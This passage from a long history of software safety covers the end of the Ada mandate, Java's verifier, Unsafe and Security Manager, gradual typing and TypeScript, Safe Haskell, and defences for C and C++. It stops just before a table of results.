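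The check worked, since the conversion failed with an exception instead of silently producing a wrong number. The disaster came from the shutdown that followed. The engineers had planned for random hardware faults, in which one unit breaks and a backup takes over, but both units ran the same program and failed in the same way. Restarting a stopped processor in flight was not feasible. The routine that failed had no purpose after lift-off, and the board thought that the units could have continued to supply their best estimates of the rocket's position. An exception stops a program from carrying on with a bad value, as a safe language is meant to ensure, but whether stopping is safe depends on what the program controls.

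The board did not blame Ada. It recommended that engineers assume software is faulty until the best current methods show it is correct, whereas the Ariane project had assumed software was correct until it was shown to be faulty.

### The end of the mandate

The National Research Council's committee, which included people from two firms that sold Ada products, published its findings in November 1996. It recommended keeping the requirement for "warfighting" software, such as weapon control, and dropping it for applications like payroll and logistics, where commercial products were better. It also told the department to either spend about $15 million a year supporting Ada or abandon the requirement. The department was already planning to cut its annual support from $10 million to almost nothing by the end of 1997.

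An industry association wanted no mandate and argued that contractors could choose a language as they chose any other component. The committee replied that the department bought systems one at a time and often lacked the expertise to reject a cheap but fragile bid. The department took the industry's side, and on 29 April 1997 Emmett Paige, the assistant secretary who had asked for the study, ended the requirement in a memorandum, *Use of the Ada Programming Language* (Department of Defense, 1997). *Ada Waivers No Longer Required by US DoD* (Kempe, 1997) reported that projects no longer needed a waiver to avoid Ada and were to choose a language on engineering grounds and lifetime cost.

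The high cost of tools explains Ada's early trouble better than it explains the end of the requirement. By 1996 Ada compilers were as good as those for comparable languages, and one was free. But many organisations had evaluated Ada in the mid-1980s, rejected it and invested in something else, and they were unwilling to reconsider it. The department had made Ada compulsory before good compilers existed, so many users first tried the language with poor ones.

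Weak enforcement allowed military software to be written in C, but stricter enforcement might not have saved the rule. The committee judged that the officials who granted waivers lacked the expertise to assess all the requests that full compliance would have produced. The mandate may also have turned some engineers against Ada. An executive at Rational, the Ada vendor that had merged with Verdix, told the trade journalist John Keller that ending the mandate could reduce engineers' hostility to the language.

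The growth of commercial software probably did most to end the mandate. In the 1970s the department could hope to lead the software market, but by the 1990s it was one large buyer among many, and the products it wanted came with C interfaces. Nextgov's *It's Ada vs. the commercial world* (1996) reported that market forces had overtaken the rule, particularly for information systems. This explanation is weaker for weapons, which had few commercial counterparts. Ada had become the most common language in weapons software, with nearly 50 million lines in use, so the mandate did have some effect. When American agencies took up memory safety again in 2022, they issued guidance rather than requiring a language.

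Ada survives mainly where a failure can kill people and the maker must produce evidence that the software is fit for use. The Boeing 777, which entered service in 1995, has flight-control software in Ada. Engineers used mathematical proof to develop the safety-critical software for the driverless Line 14 of the Paris Métro, which opened in 1998, and translated it into Ada. British air traffic controllers have used a system written largely in SPARK, a language based on Ada, since 2011.

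SPARK, first developed in Britain in the 1980s, is a subset of Ada that restricts the features hardest to reason about. Programmers use its tools to try to prove, before the program runs, that no run-time check can fail. If they succeed, they can turn the checks off without relying on the kind of informal argument that the Ariane engineers used. The proof still depends on the engineers' assumptions about the outside world. If the Ariane engineers had supplied the speeds of an Ariane 4, the proof would have been valid for Ariane 4, and Flight 501 could have failed in the same way.

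## 1995 to 2026: Java and the languages that manage memory for the programmer

Sun Microsystems released Java in 1995, two years before the Ada requirement ended, and programmers adopted it without a mandate. It had a syntax close to C's, array checks like those of Elliott ALGOL, and a garbage collector, a feature of Lisp since about 1960. Guy Steele, a Lisp expert who co-wrote Java's specification, later said that the team had been trying to win over C++ programmers and had dragged many of them about halfway to Lisp.

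### Checking the compiler's output

A Java compiler translates source code into bytecode, a set of instructions for an imaginary computer. The Java Virtual Machine (JVM) is a program that imitates this computer on a real one to run the bytecode. Sun wanted web browsers to run applets, small programs sent to visitors with a web page. A browser could not determine whether an applet's bytecode came from a trustworthy compiler or from an attacker who had written it by hand. Burroughs had handled a similar problem by running only the output of approved compilers. The JVM instead checks the bytecode itself, regardless of its source.

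This check, called verification, takes place before the code runs. JVM instructions take their operands from a stack, and the verifier works out what type of value each position on the stack will hold. Take three instructions:

```
iload_1    push an integer
aload_2    push a reference to an object
iadd       add the top two values, which must be integers
```

After the second instruction the stack holds an integer and a reference, so the verifier rejects the third. Where two branches of a program meet, the types have to be right whichever branch ran. No instruction frees an object or turns an integer into a reference, so verified code, unlike C code, cannot make up an address.

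Array indices still need a run-time check. *JEP 411* (2021), a proposal from OpenJDK, the open-source project that develops Java, describes the language's memory safety as a combination of checked array bounds, automatic deallocation and variables that always have a value before use. Of these, Ada 83 had reliably provided only checked array bounds. Java's guarantees also depend on the Java Virtual Machine (JVM) being correct, and the most widely used JVM is written largely in C++.

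### Why Java spread

Java spread mostly where C was not already established. Applets gave programmers a reason to try it, because C offered no safe way to run a stranger's program inside a browser. Oracle, which had bought Sun, dropped the browser plug-in that ran applets from its version of Java in 2018, and OpenJDK removed the remaining applet interface in 2026, according to its *JDK 26 Release Notes*.

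By then Java had long since moved to business servers. A program that processes orders spends much of its time waiting for a database or a network, so slower code matters less there than in a game. A company could also run the same bytecode on servers from different manufacturers, whereas Burroughs customers had been tied to one. The JVM ran on top of existing operating systems, so nobody had to rewrite one to use Java.

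Early JVMs interpreted bytecode one instruction at a time, which made them many times slower than compiled C. Faster hardware made up for some of the difference, and just-in-time compilers removed much of the rest by translating the busiest parts of a program into machine instructions while it ran. These compilers can also drop bounds checks that they can show are redundant, such as those in a loop that goes through an array in order. The checks remain when a program jumps around an array unpredictably, but *JEP 471* (Pressler and Buckley, 2024) describes the resulting loss of performance as small. The overhead of garbage collection was harder to reduce.

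### The price of garbage collection

Measuring a garbage collector's effect on performance is difficult because a Java program contains no instructions for freeing memory, so researchers cannot simply switch the collector off and compare. In *Quantifying the Performance of Garbage Collection vs. Explicit Memory Management*, Hertz and Berger (2005) ran each program once and recorded when it stopped using each object. Then they ran it again without a collector and freed the objects according to the record.

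The second run took place inside a simulated processor so that consulting the record would take no simulated time. Real programmers free memory somewhere between the earliest and latest possible moments, so they tried both extremes. One schedule freed each object immediately after its last use, and the other waited until the program was about to lose its last reference to the object. Programs ran at similar speeds under both schedules.

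They tested eight programs with five collectors, giving each collector between one and four times the minimum memory it needed. The best collector was generational, meaning it searched recently created objects often and older ones rarely, since most objects are needed only briefly. The table compares it with a standard C memory allocator on the later of the two schedules.

| Memory used, relative to manual management | Running time, relative to manual management |
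|---|---|
| 2.1 times | 1.69 times |
| 2.5 times | 1.30 times |
| 2.9 times | 1.17 times |
| 3.5 times | 1.10 times |
| 5.1 times | 1.00 times |

With plenty of spare memory, a program ran as fast under garbage collection as under manual management, but with little spare memory it ran much slower. Even in the smallest workable heap, the collector used twice as much memory as manual management did. Adding memory made the collector run less often, and the first additions helped most. When the computer ran out of physical memory and had to move data to disk, garbage collection was about ten times slower than manual management.

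To check that the Java setup itself was not the cause, they added manual freeing to the memory system used by one of the collectors. This modified system ran only 4% slower on average than the C allocator. They also repeated some of the tests on a real computer and saw the same pattern.

The experiment favored manual management in one respect, since its simulated programmer never freed an object too early or forgot to free one. But the programs had been written for a garbage collector, and their programmers might have used memory differently in C. The programs were also small by today's standards, with at most 33 megabytes of reachable data.

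These numbers help explain who stayed with C and C++. Makers of small devices had little memory to spare, and web browsers had to share memory with every other program on the user's machine. Game developers also had to worry about pauses. Games draw a new frame many times a second, and all five collectors stopped the program while they worked, so a frame could arrive late even if the program was fast on average. Newer collectors do most of their work while the program runs, which shortens the pauses but still takes spare memory. Operating-system kernels have a different problem because they have to manage the memory that a collector would run in.

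Some developers who did choose Java kept part of their data in memory that the JVM's garbage collector does not manage. The makers of Hadoop and Cassandra, two systems for storing and processing very large amounts of data, did this and used one of Java's escape hatches to release that memory promptly.

### The escape hatches

Java has had a foreign function interface, the Java Native Interface (JNI), since its second release, and C code called through it can break any of Java's guarantees. OpenJDK's *JEP 472* (2023) gives the example of a C function that uses a number from Java as an address and stores a 3 there. This may overwrite memory that the JVM depends on, and the JVM may crash long after the function has finished. Native code can also write past the end of a Java array or alter a string that Java programmers assume cannot change.

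Java's developers added the other main escape hatch, a class named `sun.misc.Unsafe`, in 2002 for use only in their own libraries. Of its 87 methods, 79 access memory without safety checks. One of these can store an integer in a field that should hold a reference, which makes the field point to an arbitrary address. The developers intended to do their own checks before each call and to offer safe replacements later. They had no way at the time to stop other people from using the class. Its constructor was private, but a programmer could get past that in a few lines of code.

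Library authors soon found that `Unsafe` made their code faster. Since 2006 the Java compiler has printed a warning, which programmers cannot turn off, that the class may be removed in a future release. By 2015 many libraries relied on it anyway. For *Use at Your Own Risk*, Mastrangelo, Ponzanelli and colleagues searched 86,479 archives of compiled code from Maven Central, the largest public collection of Java libraries. Only 817 of them, about 1%, used `Unsafe` directly, but 21,297, or 25%, depended on one that did, sometimes through several other libraries. The count missed code that reached `Unsafe` by indirect means, and it included some dependencies that a program listed but may never have used.

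They then read the source code of the 100 most widely relied-on archives that used `Unsafe`, and sorted the uses into 14 patterns. These were among the most important:

- Creating an object without running its constructor, the code that normally sets it up. Testing tools do this, as do libraries that rebuild objects from saved data. Archives that did this had 14,794 others depending on them.
- Reading an array of bytes eight at a time, for speed.
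- Updating a value shared between threads in a single step that no other thread can interrupt, so that no thread has to wait for a lock.
- Changing fields that the programmer had declared `final`, meaning fixed once set.

Many of these authors had good reasons to use `Unsafe`, since standard Java offered no equivalent or only a slower one, but others did not. Pressler and Buckley blame some of the use on code copied from online forums, and note that `Unsafe` can make a program slower by preventing the JVM from optimising it.

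An Ada reviewer could look for unsafe operations by searching a project for the word "Unchecked". In Java, a search of an application's source code for `Unsafe` could miss a call in a compiled library that another library had brought in. The application's developer then relied on a programmer they had never heard of to make that call safely.

### Closing the hatches

Oracle planned to hide `Unsafe` in Java 9. In response, *What to do about sun.misc.Unsafe* (Luck, Engelbert and colleagues, 2015), written by a group of Java vendors and users, listed the products that relied on the class and called for replacements before it was hidden. Oracle relented, and Reinhold explained in *The Secret History and Tragic Fate of sun.misc.Unsafe* (2015) that the class would remain available while Oracle developed supported alternatives. Java 9 brought the first of these in 2017, for memory that the garbage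 collector manages. The replacement for other memory became final only in Java 22, in 2024.

By then the developers had a general policy, which Pressler, Buckley and Reinhold's *JEP draft* (2023) calls "integrity by default". Suppose a class keeps a counter that is always even, because its only public operations add or subtract two. A library that restores saved objects can write an odd number straight into the counter's private field. Any code that relies on the counter being even may then go wrong, and nobody can rule this out without reading all the code in the application. Under the policy, only the application's developer can permit a library to do such things, by naming it when the program starts. Including the library does not count as permission, because the developer may not know what it does, or even that it is there.

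The policy covers `Unsafe`, native code, agents (here, tools that rewrite a program's code as it runs) and the use of reflection to reach private fields. It would also benefit programs that use none of these. OpenJDK's *JEP 500* points out that the JVM cannot assume that any `final` field is constant while some library might change it, so it misses optimisations in every program.

Java's developers introduce each restriction in stages because so much software would otherwise break. First Java allows the operation silently, then it prints a warning, and finally it refuses unless the application's developer has given permission. `Unsafe` will eventually have no such permission, because Java's developers intend to delete its memory methods. In Java 23, released in 2024, they marked all 79 for removal. Java 24 began to print a warning the first time a program used one, and Pressler and Buckley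 (2024), in *JEP 498*, scheduled the refusals for "JDK 26 or later", with deletion to follow. Inside Java's *Peaceful and Bright Future of Integrity by Default in Java* (2025) had pointed to Java 26 itself. The other hatches are also at the warning stage. In February 2026, slides from Oracle (2026) listed a warning as the default for native code, since Java 24, and for changes to `final` fields, from Java 26. JEP 472 leaves refusals for native code to an unspecified future release.

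A library author objected on OpenJDK's issue tracker that the warnings would not work as intended. People who use a library cannot fix it, so the author expected most of them to add the option that silences the warnings. That option will stop working once refusal becomes the default, although developers will still be able to go back to warnings for a time.

### Holes in the guarantee

Java has also had unintended soundness holes. In 1997 Vijay Saraswat, a researcher at AT&T, published a note titled *Java is not type-safe*. The problem lay in class loaders, the components that fetch a class's code when a program first needs it. A program can supply its own loader, and two loaders can fetch different classes with the same name. The JVM was supposed to treat these as different types, but in some cases it compared only the names. Code could therefore receive an object of one class and treat it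 as the other, for instance by reading a private field as if it were public. Sheng Liang and Gilad Bracha at Sun published a fix in 1998. The JVM now records when two loaders share a class name, and raises an error if the name refers to a different class in each.

Java's designers knew about another gap from the start and covered it with a run-time check:

```java
String[] names = new String[1];
Object[] things = names;
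things[0] = 7;
```

The compiler accepts all three lines. It treats an array of strings as an array of objects, although an array of objects may hold a number and an array of strings may not. The designers allowed this so that one routine could sort or copy arrays of many types, which Pascal programmers had been unable to do. The JVM makes up for it by checking the type of what a program stores in such an array, and the third line raises an exception. (TypeScript, which adds types to JavaScript, has the same rule for arrays but no such check.)

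The third gap lasted twelve years before anyone reported it. In 2004 Java gained generics, which let a programmer write one list class and use it for strings or numbers. In 2016 Nada Amin and Ross Tate published a short program that used generics to turn a value of any type into any other without a complaint from the compiler. At its centre is a class that takes two types, and that Java permits only if the second is a subtype of the first:

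```java
class Constrain<A, B extends A> {}
...
Constrain<U, ? super T> c = null;
```

The question mark stands for some unnamed type X. The declaration says that T is a subtype of X, and the rule for the class says that X is a subtype of U. The compiler concludes that T is a subtype of U:

T <: X <: U, and hence T <: U.

If T is the type of integers and U is the type of strings, no such X exists, so no matching `Constrain` object can exist either. But Java accepts `null`, the reference to nothing, as a value of every reference type, including this impossible one. The program can then use `c` to treat an integer as a string.

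Researchers had proved parts of Java's type system sound, but their simplified models left out `null`. The consequences were mild because the JVM does not rely on generic types. The compiler inserts an ordinary run-time type check where the program uses the result. As with arrays, this check catches the error that static checking missed. It raises an exception, and an attacker gains no access to memory.

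### The Security Manager

A memory-safe applet could still delete a visitor's files by calling the ordinary library routine for deleting files. Java therefore included a second kind of protection, the Security Manager, from its first release. Before opening a file or a network connection, the Java library called the Security Manager, which could block the operation. At first, the Security Manager let code from the visitor's own computer do anything and code from the web do almost nothing.

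Java 1.2 replaced this in 1998 with permissions for each piece of code, following the principle of least privilege, under which code gets only the access it needs. All the code ran in one process, so the Security Manager had to work out on whose behalf a request came. It did this by inspecting the call stack, the list of functions that have started and not yet finished. Suppose a stranger's plug-in asks a report library to save a file:

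```
FileOutputStream   Java's own library     may do anything
ReportWriter       the report library     may write files
Plugin             a stranger's code      may not write files
```

Java's library makes the request and is allowed to write files, but that is not enough. If P₁ to Pₙ are the sets of permissions of the functions on the stack, the Security Manager allows an action only if its permission is in

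P₁ ∩ P₂ ∩ … ∩ Pₙ.

It refuses the request because the plug-in lacks the permission. Otherwise the plug-in could get around its restrictions by asking more trusted code to act for it.

The rule was sometimes too strict. A program that asked for the current time might cause Java's library to read its own time-zone file, even if the program had no permission to read files. The library could mark such an action as privileged. The inspection then stopped at the function that made the mark, without checking the permissions of its callers. Every such mark was an escape hatch, and its author had to be sure that no caller could misuse it. Mullan and Buckley report in *JEP 486* that more than 1,000 methods in Java's libraries had to check permissions, and more than 1,200 had to raise their own permissions.

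The Security Manager was off by default for ordinary applications, partly because the inspections were slow. A developer who turned it on had to list every permission the program needed, and could not restrict file reading without restricting everything else too. Developers usually had to give a library's permissions to the application as well, because the application was also on the stack. Granting every permission was easiest, and in Mullan and Buckley's experience, most of the few people who enabled the Security Manager did that. People who answer permission prompts from AI agents face the same temptation.

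Java's developers marked the Security Manager for removal in 2021 and heard hardly any complaints. Java 24 permanently disabled it in 2025, though an empty version of its interface remains so that old programs still run. OpenJDK argued that applets had disappeared, few people had ever used the Security Manager on servers, and it could not address 19 of the 25 most dangerous kinds of software weakness on a 2020 industry list. In many attacks now, the attacker sends malicious data to a program that has all the right permissions but mishandles the data.

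Memory safety caused its users none of these difficulties. It was always on, and an array's bounds are the same whoever is running the program, so nobody had to write a policy. By contrast, somebody has to decide which files a program should be able to read, because that depends on the program's purpose.

Mullan and Buckley recommend that developers confine Java programs with tools outside Java, such as containers, which limit what a whole process can reach. These tools are easier to use and far more popular than Java's Security Manager. But a container cannot give a plug-in fewer rights than the program it runs in unless the developer moves the plug-in to its own process. Firmstone's *Why JEP 411 Will Have a Negative Impact on Java Security* opposed removing the Security Manager, citing the principle of least privilege. Java's developers decided not to provide a replacement.

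## 2006 to 2026: adding types to languages that had none

JavaScript came out in 1995, the same year as Java, and became the language of the web. Like Python and most Lisps, it checks types only while a program runs. A variable can hold a number and later hold text, and an operation on the wrong kind of value raises an exception or gives an odd result. These languages are memory-safe and suit small programs well, but in a large program a mistake may stay hidden until a user triggers it. Companies that had built large systems this way could rarely afford to rewrite them in Java, so researchers looked for a way to add types to a program one piece at a time.

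### A type that matches anything

A bibliography of the field, *gradual typing bib*, credits four papers from 2006 and 2007 with independently introducing gradual typing. One of them, *Gradual Typing for Functional Languages* (Siek and Taha, 2006), gave the idea its name. The paper's design lets programmers mix checked and unchecked code in one program by declaring types where they want checking and leaving them out elsewhere.

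Anything without a declared type gets the unknown type, written "?". An ordinary checker requires the type of an argument to equal the type the function expects. Siek and Taha require only that the two be consistent, written ~, which means that their known parts agree:

- τ ~ τ, τ ~ ? and ? ~ τ, for every type τ.
- (σ₁ → σ₂) ~ (τ₁ → τ₂) if σ₁ ~ τ₁ and σ₂ ~ τ₂.

Take a function that adds one to x. If the programmer has declared x to be a number, the checker rejects a call that passes `true`. If x has no declared type, the checker accepts the call, and the program fails when it runs.

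Two types can each be consistent with "?" without being consistent with each other, as with numbers and truth values. Otherwise every type would match every other, and the checker would accept everything. Siek and Taha had first tried an older design that treated the unknown type as a supertype of all the others. That design let the bad call through, because the checker could treat `true` as a value of unknown type and then treat that value as a number.

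The compiler inserts a run-time check, called a cast, wherever a value of unknown type reaches a place with a declared type. Siek and Taha proved that if such a program finishes, it produces either a value of the expected type or a cast error. This is close to Milner's guarantee, but it also allows the cast error. A program with types everywhere needs no casts, and the checker finds every error an ordinary type checker would.

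### The price of checking every boundary

A cast can check immediately whether a value is a number, but it can't check whether a function always returns a number, because no inspection can determine that in general. Instead, the language wraps the function in a second one that checks the arguments and results of every later call, so if typed code calls an untyped function a million times, the program runs the check a million times.

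Takikawa, Feltey and colleagues (2016), in *Is Sound Gradual Typing Dead?*, measured how much this slows programs in Typed Racket, a gradually typed relative of Lisp in which each module is either typed or untyped. They took twelve programs of 2 to 16 modules and wrote a typed and an untyped version of each module. They then timed all 2ⁿ possible mixtures for a program with n modules, running each 30 times. Earlier studies had mostly compared fully untyped programs with fully typed ones, but a team converting a large system spends most of its time working with a mixture.

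One of the programs searches for the longest piece of text that two strings share. It has six modules, and a programmer might add types to them in this order:

| Modules with types | Running time, relative to no types |
|---|---|
| None | 1 |
| `label` | 88 |
| `label`, `structs` | 104 |
| `label`, `structs`, `main` | 104 |
| `label`, `structs`, `main`, `ukkonen` | 99 |
| All except `data` | 103 |
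| All six | 0.7 |

The finished program is faster than the original because the compiler can use the types to optimise it. But to reach it, the programmer has to go through five versions that are too slow to ship. In the slowest mixture, the program spent 94% of its time on checks. Only 6 of the 64 mixtures ran in at most three times the original's running time, a limit that Takikawa and colleagues already considered generous.

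Two of the twelve programs never took twice as long as the untyped version, whatever the mixture, while four had mixtures that took more than 100 times as long. Takikawa and colleagues concluded that sound gradual typing was dead, given the compilers of the time. They also noted that Typed Racket's compiler did not optimise the checks, and that about a fifth of the checking time was spent on functions that obviously return true or false, to confirm that they did.

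Later work confirmed that caveat. *Sound gradual typing: only mostly dead* (2017) reran the benchmarks on an experimental just-in-time compiler, which removed more than 90% of the overhead on typical programs, though some stayed slow. Other researchers have used a tool to prove in advance that many of the checks cannot fail, or have designed new languages in which the checks take little time, though a new language doesn't help people who already have a large JavaScript codebase.

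### TypeScript drops the run-time checks

Microsoft released TypeScript in 2012. It is JavaScript with optional types, and its version of "?" is a type named `any`. In their published design goals, TypeScript's developers list a sound type system as a non-goal. They wanted to balance correctness and productivity. They also wanted the compiler to erase the types completely, so that the program runs as plain JavaScript and behaves exactly as it would without them.

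This makes TypeScript cheap to adopt, because adding a type can't slow a program down or break it. It also means that nothing checks a value when it passes from `any` to a declared type:

```typescript
const order: any = JSON.parse('{"price": "20"}');
const price: number = order.price;
const total = price + 5;
console.log(total.toFixed(2));
```

The first line reads an order that arrived as text, with quotation marks around the price. The compiler accepts the second line, since `any` matches `number`, but `price` now holds the text "20". In the third line JavaScript joins the two values as text, so `total` is "205" instead of 25. The program fails in the last line, because text has no `toFixed` operation. In a real system these lines may be in four different files, and the error message points only to the last. If the program had saved the total instead of formatting it, the customer might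 have received a bill for 205. Under Siek and Taha's rules, the program would have stopped at the second line.

TypeScript has no run-time checks like those that back up Java's generic types. Avoiding `any` does not restore the guarantee, because the type system is unsound in other places too. TypeScript's website links to a list of them. Types for existing JavaScript libraries are another weak point, because volunteers write many of them by hand and the compiler does not check them against the library's code.

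Soundness would have made programs much slower for TypeScript's first users. Takikawa and colleagues quote measurements of Safe TypeScript, an experimental sound version of the language. Fully typed programs ran only 6.5% slower on average, but programs without type declarations, which every JavaScript team starts with, ran 22 times slower.

Dropping soundness was tolerable in TypeScript because JavaScript is memory-safe, so a value of the wrong type does not corrupt memory as it can in C.

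### What an unsound checker catches

Even without a guarantee, the checker finds many mistakes. In *To Type or Not to Type*, Gao, Bird and Barr (2017) estimated how many by studying a random sample of 400 bugs that programmers had already fixed in JavaScript projects on GitHub. For each bug, they retrieved the code from just before the fix, added types to the part that the fix changed, and ran two checkers, TypeScript and Facebook's similar Flow. They counted a bug as caught if the checker reported an error there and a correct program could have had the added types.

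Each checker caught 60 of the 400 bugs, or 15% (95% confidence interval 11.5 to 18.5%), and the two caught mostly the same ones. About 78% of the bugs that both missed were failures to do what the specification required, such as a wrong condition. These type systems cannot express such requirements.

The figure probably understates the benefit, since these bugs had already survived the programmer's own testing and often a colleague's review. But Gao and colleagues knew where each bug was, and a programmer would have had to add types without knowing. With that advantage, they needed an average of only 2.4 extra symbols per bug in TypeScript. Much of TypeScript's success came from a new option in version 2.0 to warn about values that might be missing, which raised the number of bugs it caught by 58% over version 1.8. The developers had strengthened the checker after people were already using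 it, and they had made the stricter rule optional.

It is harder to show that projects in typed languages have fewer bugs overall. Baishakhi Ray and colleagues tried in *A Large-Scale Study of Programming Languages and Code Quality in GitHub* (2014). They collected 729 projects in 17 languages and counted a change as a bug fix if its description contained a word such as "error" or "fix". After adjusting for each project's age, size and number of developers, they linked 11 of the languages to unusually many or few fixes, with the fewest for TypeScript.

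*On the Impact of Programming Languages on Code Quality* (Berger, Hollenbeck and colleagues, 2019) re-examined the data. The earliest change labelled as TypeScript dated from 2003, nine years before the language's release. TypeScript files end in `.ts`, but so do files that hold translations of a program's menus, and these had been counted as TypeScript. Only 16 of the 41 projects labelled as TypeScript contained any, and the three largest of those contained only type declarations. The search for "fix", meant to find bug fixes, had also matched a change about "infix operators". Independent developers reread 400 of the changes and judged that 36% of those labelled as bug fixes were not bug fixes. After corrections, only four of the 11 associations remained, all very small.

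Ray, Devanbu and Filkov (2019), in *Rebuttal to Berger et al., TOPLAS 2019*, replied that they had always called the effects small and had warned against reading them as causal. They had also found the TypeScript mistake soon after publication, and their 2017 version reported no significant result for TypeScript. *FSE/CACM Rebuttal²* (2019) continued the argument. Both sides accept that the true effect may be zero. However, Berger and colleagues found 26 citations that described the result as cause and effect, and four that did not.

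A later paper, also titled *To Type or Not to Type* (2022), even found that bug fixes made up a larger share of changes in TypeScript projects than in JavaScript ones, 21% against 13%. Perhaps teams choose TypeScript for harder programs, or record their fixes more carefully. Gao's experiment avoids such differences by testing the same code with and without types, so it is better evidence that the checker catches real mistakes. It cannot show how many bugs a team using TypeScript ends up with, because programmers who rely on a checker may test less.

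### Why programmers took it up

Anders Hejlsberg, who led TypeScript's design, once thought it might attract a quarter of JavaScript programmers, according to GitHub's *TypeScript's rise in the AI era* (2025). In August 2025, TypeScript overtook Python and JavaScript to become the most-used language on GitHub. Linuxiac's *TypeScript Overtakes Python to Become GitHub's #1 Programming Language in 2025* (2025) reports 2.63 million TypeScript contributors, about 42,000 more than Python had and 66% more than a year earlier. The ranking counts people who contributed code in a language, so it does not measure how strictly they used the types.

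Leo Meyerovich and Ariel Rabkin's *Empirical Analysis of Programming Language Adoption* (2013) helps explain this growth, although it appeared when TypeScript was still new. They analysed more than 200,000 open-source projects and several surveys of 1,000 to 13,000 programmers each. Programmers choosing a language for a project were influenced most by the available open-source libraries, their existing code and the languages they already knew, and much less by reliability and performance. They also valued expressing ideas easily more than correctness, and saw static types mainly as an aid to correctness. The surveys rely on programmers' own accounts of their choices, which may differ from their actual reasons.

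TypeScript left all three of the strongest influences in place. A team could rename a JavaScript file, keep its libraries and add types when it had time. Teams adopting Ada had needed new tools, libraries and training before they saw any benefit. Programmers also benefited from TypeScript immediately, because an editor can use the types to complete names and find every use of a function.

In return they gave up being able to rely on a declaration. In TypeScript, `price: number` records what the programmer believed, whereas a sound language would guarantee that `price` is a number when the program runs. Anyone who needs to be sure must still write a run-time check, especially for data from outside the program. TypeScript was still a clear gain for teams whose alternative was plain JavaScript, which had no such guarantee either. It would be inadequate for anyone who needs protection from an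 adversary. Catching 15% of accidental bugs is useful, but an attacker can look for one of the others, and someone writing a malicious module can avoid the type checks by writing `any`.

### Safe Haskell

Haskell's developers went in the opposite direction, from a strict language with an escape hatch to a subset without one. In Haskell, a function's type shows whether it can affect the outside world. A function of type `String -> String` can only compute one text from another, while anything that reads a file or uses the network has `IO` in its type. Running a stranger's `String -> String` function should therefore be harmless, but the standard libraries include this:

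```haskell
unsafePerformIO :: IO a -> a
```

Haskell's `unsafePerformIO` performs an action and removes `IO` from its type. Library authors use it for good reasons, such as calling a C routine that only does arithmetic. A malicious author could use it to delete files from inside a function whose type shows no side effects, and careless use can turn a value of one type into another.

*Safe Haskell* (2012), by David Terei, Simon Marlow and colleagues, describes the remedy, which the main Haskell compiler has included since 2011. The compiler stops a module marked `Safe` from importing any unsafe module, including the one that provides `unsafePerformIO`. A module marked `Trustworthy` may use unsafe features internally if its author vouches that code outside the module cannot misuse them. The person compiling the program can choose which packages to trust. Odersky and colleagues' restricted Scala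 for AI agents has a similar arrangement.

Removing the named escape hatches was not enough, because a convenience feature in Haskell, generalised newtype deriving, had a soundness hole that let programmers convert between types illegally. Safe Haskell banned the feature at first, then allowed it after the compiler's developers closed the hole.

A website that runs visitors' code can define its own restricted version of `IO`, with operations that read files only from one directory. Visitors' modules must be `Safe` and must use the restricted type, so they cannot access the rest of the disk. They can still loop forever or use up the machine's memory, which the website must prevent by other means.

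Safe Haskell has remained a specialist feature. Existing Haskell programs could keep using `unsafePerformIO` and did not have to change, but library authors had to mark and review their modules, mostly to benefit the few people who run untrusted code.

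## 1993 to 2026: protecting C and C++ without replacing them

TypeScript spread because teams could keep the JavaScript they already had. Owners of C and C++ programs had even stronger reasons to keep theirs. *It is time to standardize principles and practices for software memory safety* (Watson, Baldwin and colleagues, 2025) quotes an industry estimate that rewriting a billion lines of code costs about $1 trillion. *CHERI Myths*, a post from CHERIoT, a project that designs secure processors for small devices, estimates that there are around ten billion lines of C and C++ in open-source software alone. Some of that code would be hard to rewrite even with enough money. For example, rewriting a video decoder without making it slower would require someone expert in both video compression and the new language.

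Engineers who wanted to keep C code have tried three approaches: making its memory errors harder to exploit, adding the missing checks, and confining a program so that its errors damage only that program.

### Making errors harder to exploit

An attack like the Morris worm's on the finger server takes several steps, from overflowing an array to running the attacker's instructions. Engineers can block any one of them without finding the bug. *SoK* (2013), by Szekeres, Payer and colleagues, surveys these defences and how attackers get past them.

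Stack canaries protect the return address, where the program resumes after a function finishes. When a function starts, it places a secret random number, the canary, between its local arrays and the return address, and it checks the number before returning. Text that runs off the end of an array changes the canary on its way to the return address, so the check fails and the program stops. A canary would have stopped the finger attack. But an attacker who controls an array index can write directly to the return address without changing the canary.

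Processors can also mark each region of memory as writable or executable, but not both. The worm's instructions arrived as data, so this protection would have stopped them from running. Attackers responded by reusing code already in memory. In return-oriented programming, they fill the stack with the addresses of short code fragments that each end in a return instruction. Each return starts the next fragment. The standard C library usually contains enough fragments to perform any computation.

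An attacker has to know where code is to reuse it, so address randomisation loads code and data at different places each time. But a memory error can also reveal an address. In several attacks on browsers from 2012, a script overwrote the recorded length of a piece of text, then read far past the text's real end until it found a usable address.

Control-flow integrity checks jumps whose destination the program looks up in memory. The compiler lists in advance where each such jump could legitimately go, and the program stops if the destination is not on the list. The original version, from 2005, allowed any call through a function pointer to reach any function that the program ever called that way, so an attacker could still swap one such function for another.

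An attacker may not need to redirect the program at all:

```c
struct user {
    char name[8];
    bool is_admin;
};
```

Suppose a server copies nine bytes of a visitor's name into `name`. The ninth byte overwrites `is_admin`, and the server treats the visitor as an administrator. The return address is unchanged and the program runs only its own code, in the intended order, so none of the four defences stops the attack.

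### Adding the missing checks

A bounds check requires the array's start and end, but a C pointer holds only an address. CCured and Cyclone, two safe versions of C from 2002, used wider pointers that also stored these limits, much as Burroughs descriptors had. Programmers had to annotate their source code, and libraries compiled in the ordinary way could not use the wider pointers.

SoftBound (2009) left pointers the same size and kept their limits in a separate table. Before the program uses a pointer p to reach k bytes, it looks up the limits and tests that

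base(p) ≤ p and p + k ≤ end(p).

SoftBound provably catches every out-of-bounds access if every part of the program has the checks. If an unprotected library changes a pointer, the table still holds the old limits, and the next check may stop a correct program. SoftBound also does not detect the use of freed memory. The CETS extension detects it by giving each allocation a unique number and recording whether that allocation is still in use. Together they make C fully memory-safe, but programs take more than twice as long to run.

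Other researchers stored limits for each object (a block of memory) instead of each pointer. This works better with unprotected libraries, because a library can change a pointer without making the object's limits wrong. But these checkers allow any access that stays inside the object, so they miss the overflow from `name` into `is_admin`. They cannot forbid every write that crosses from one field into another, because C lets a program clear a whole structure through one pointer.

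AddressSanitizer (2012) marks memory that the program should not touch, including blocks it has just freed, and checks accesses against the marks. It misses the use of a freed block if the program has already allocated that memory again. Programs run 73% slower with it, so developers use it mainly for testing, where it finds only the errors that a test triggers. In slides on C++ safety, Google (2025) reported that it had learned the size of the problem from such tools, but that they were not enough for about a billion lines of code.

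### The deployment threshold

Szekeres and colleagues compared the cost of each defence with whether anybody used it in practice. These are some of their results:

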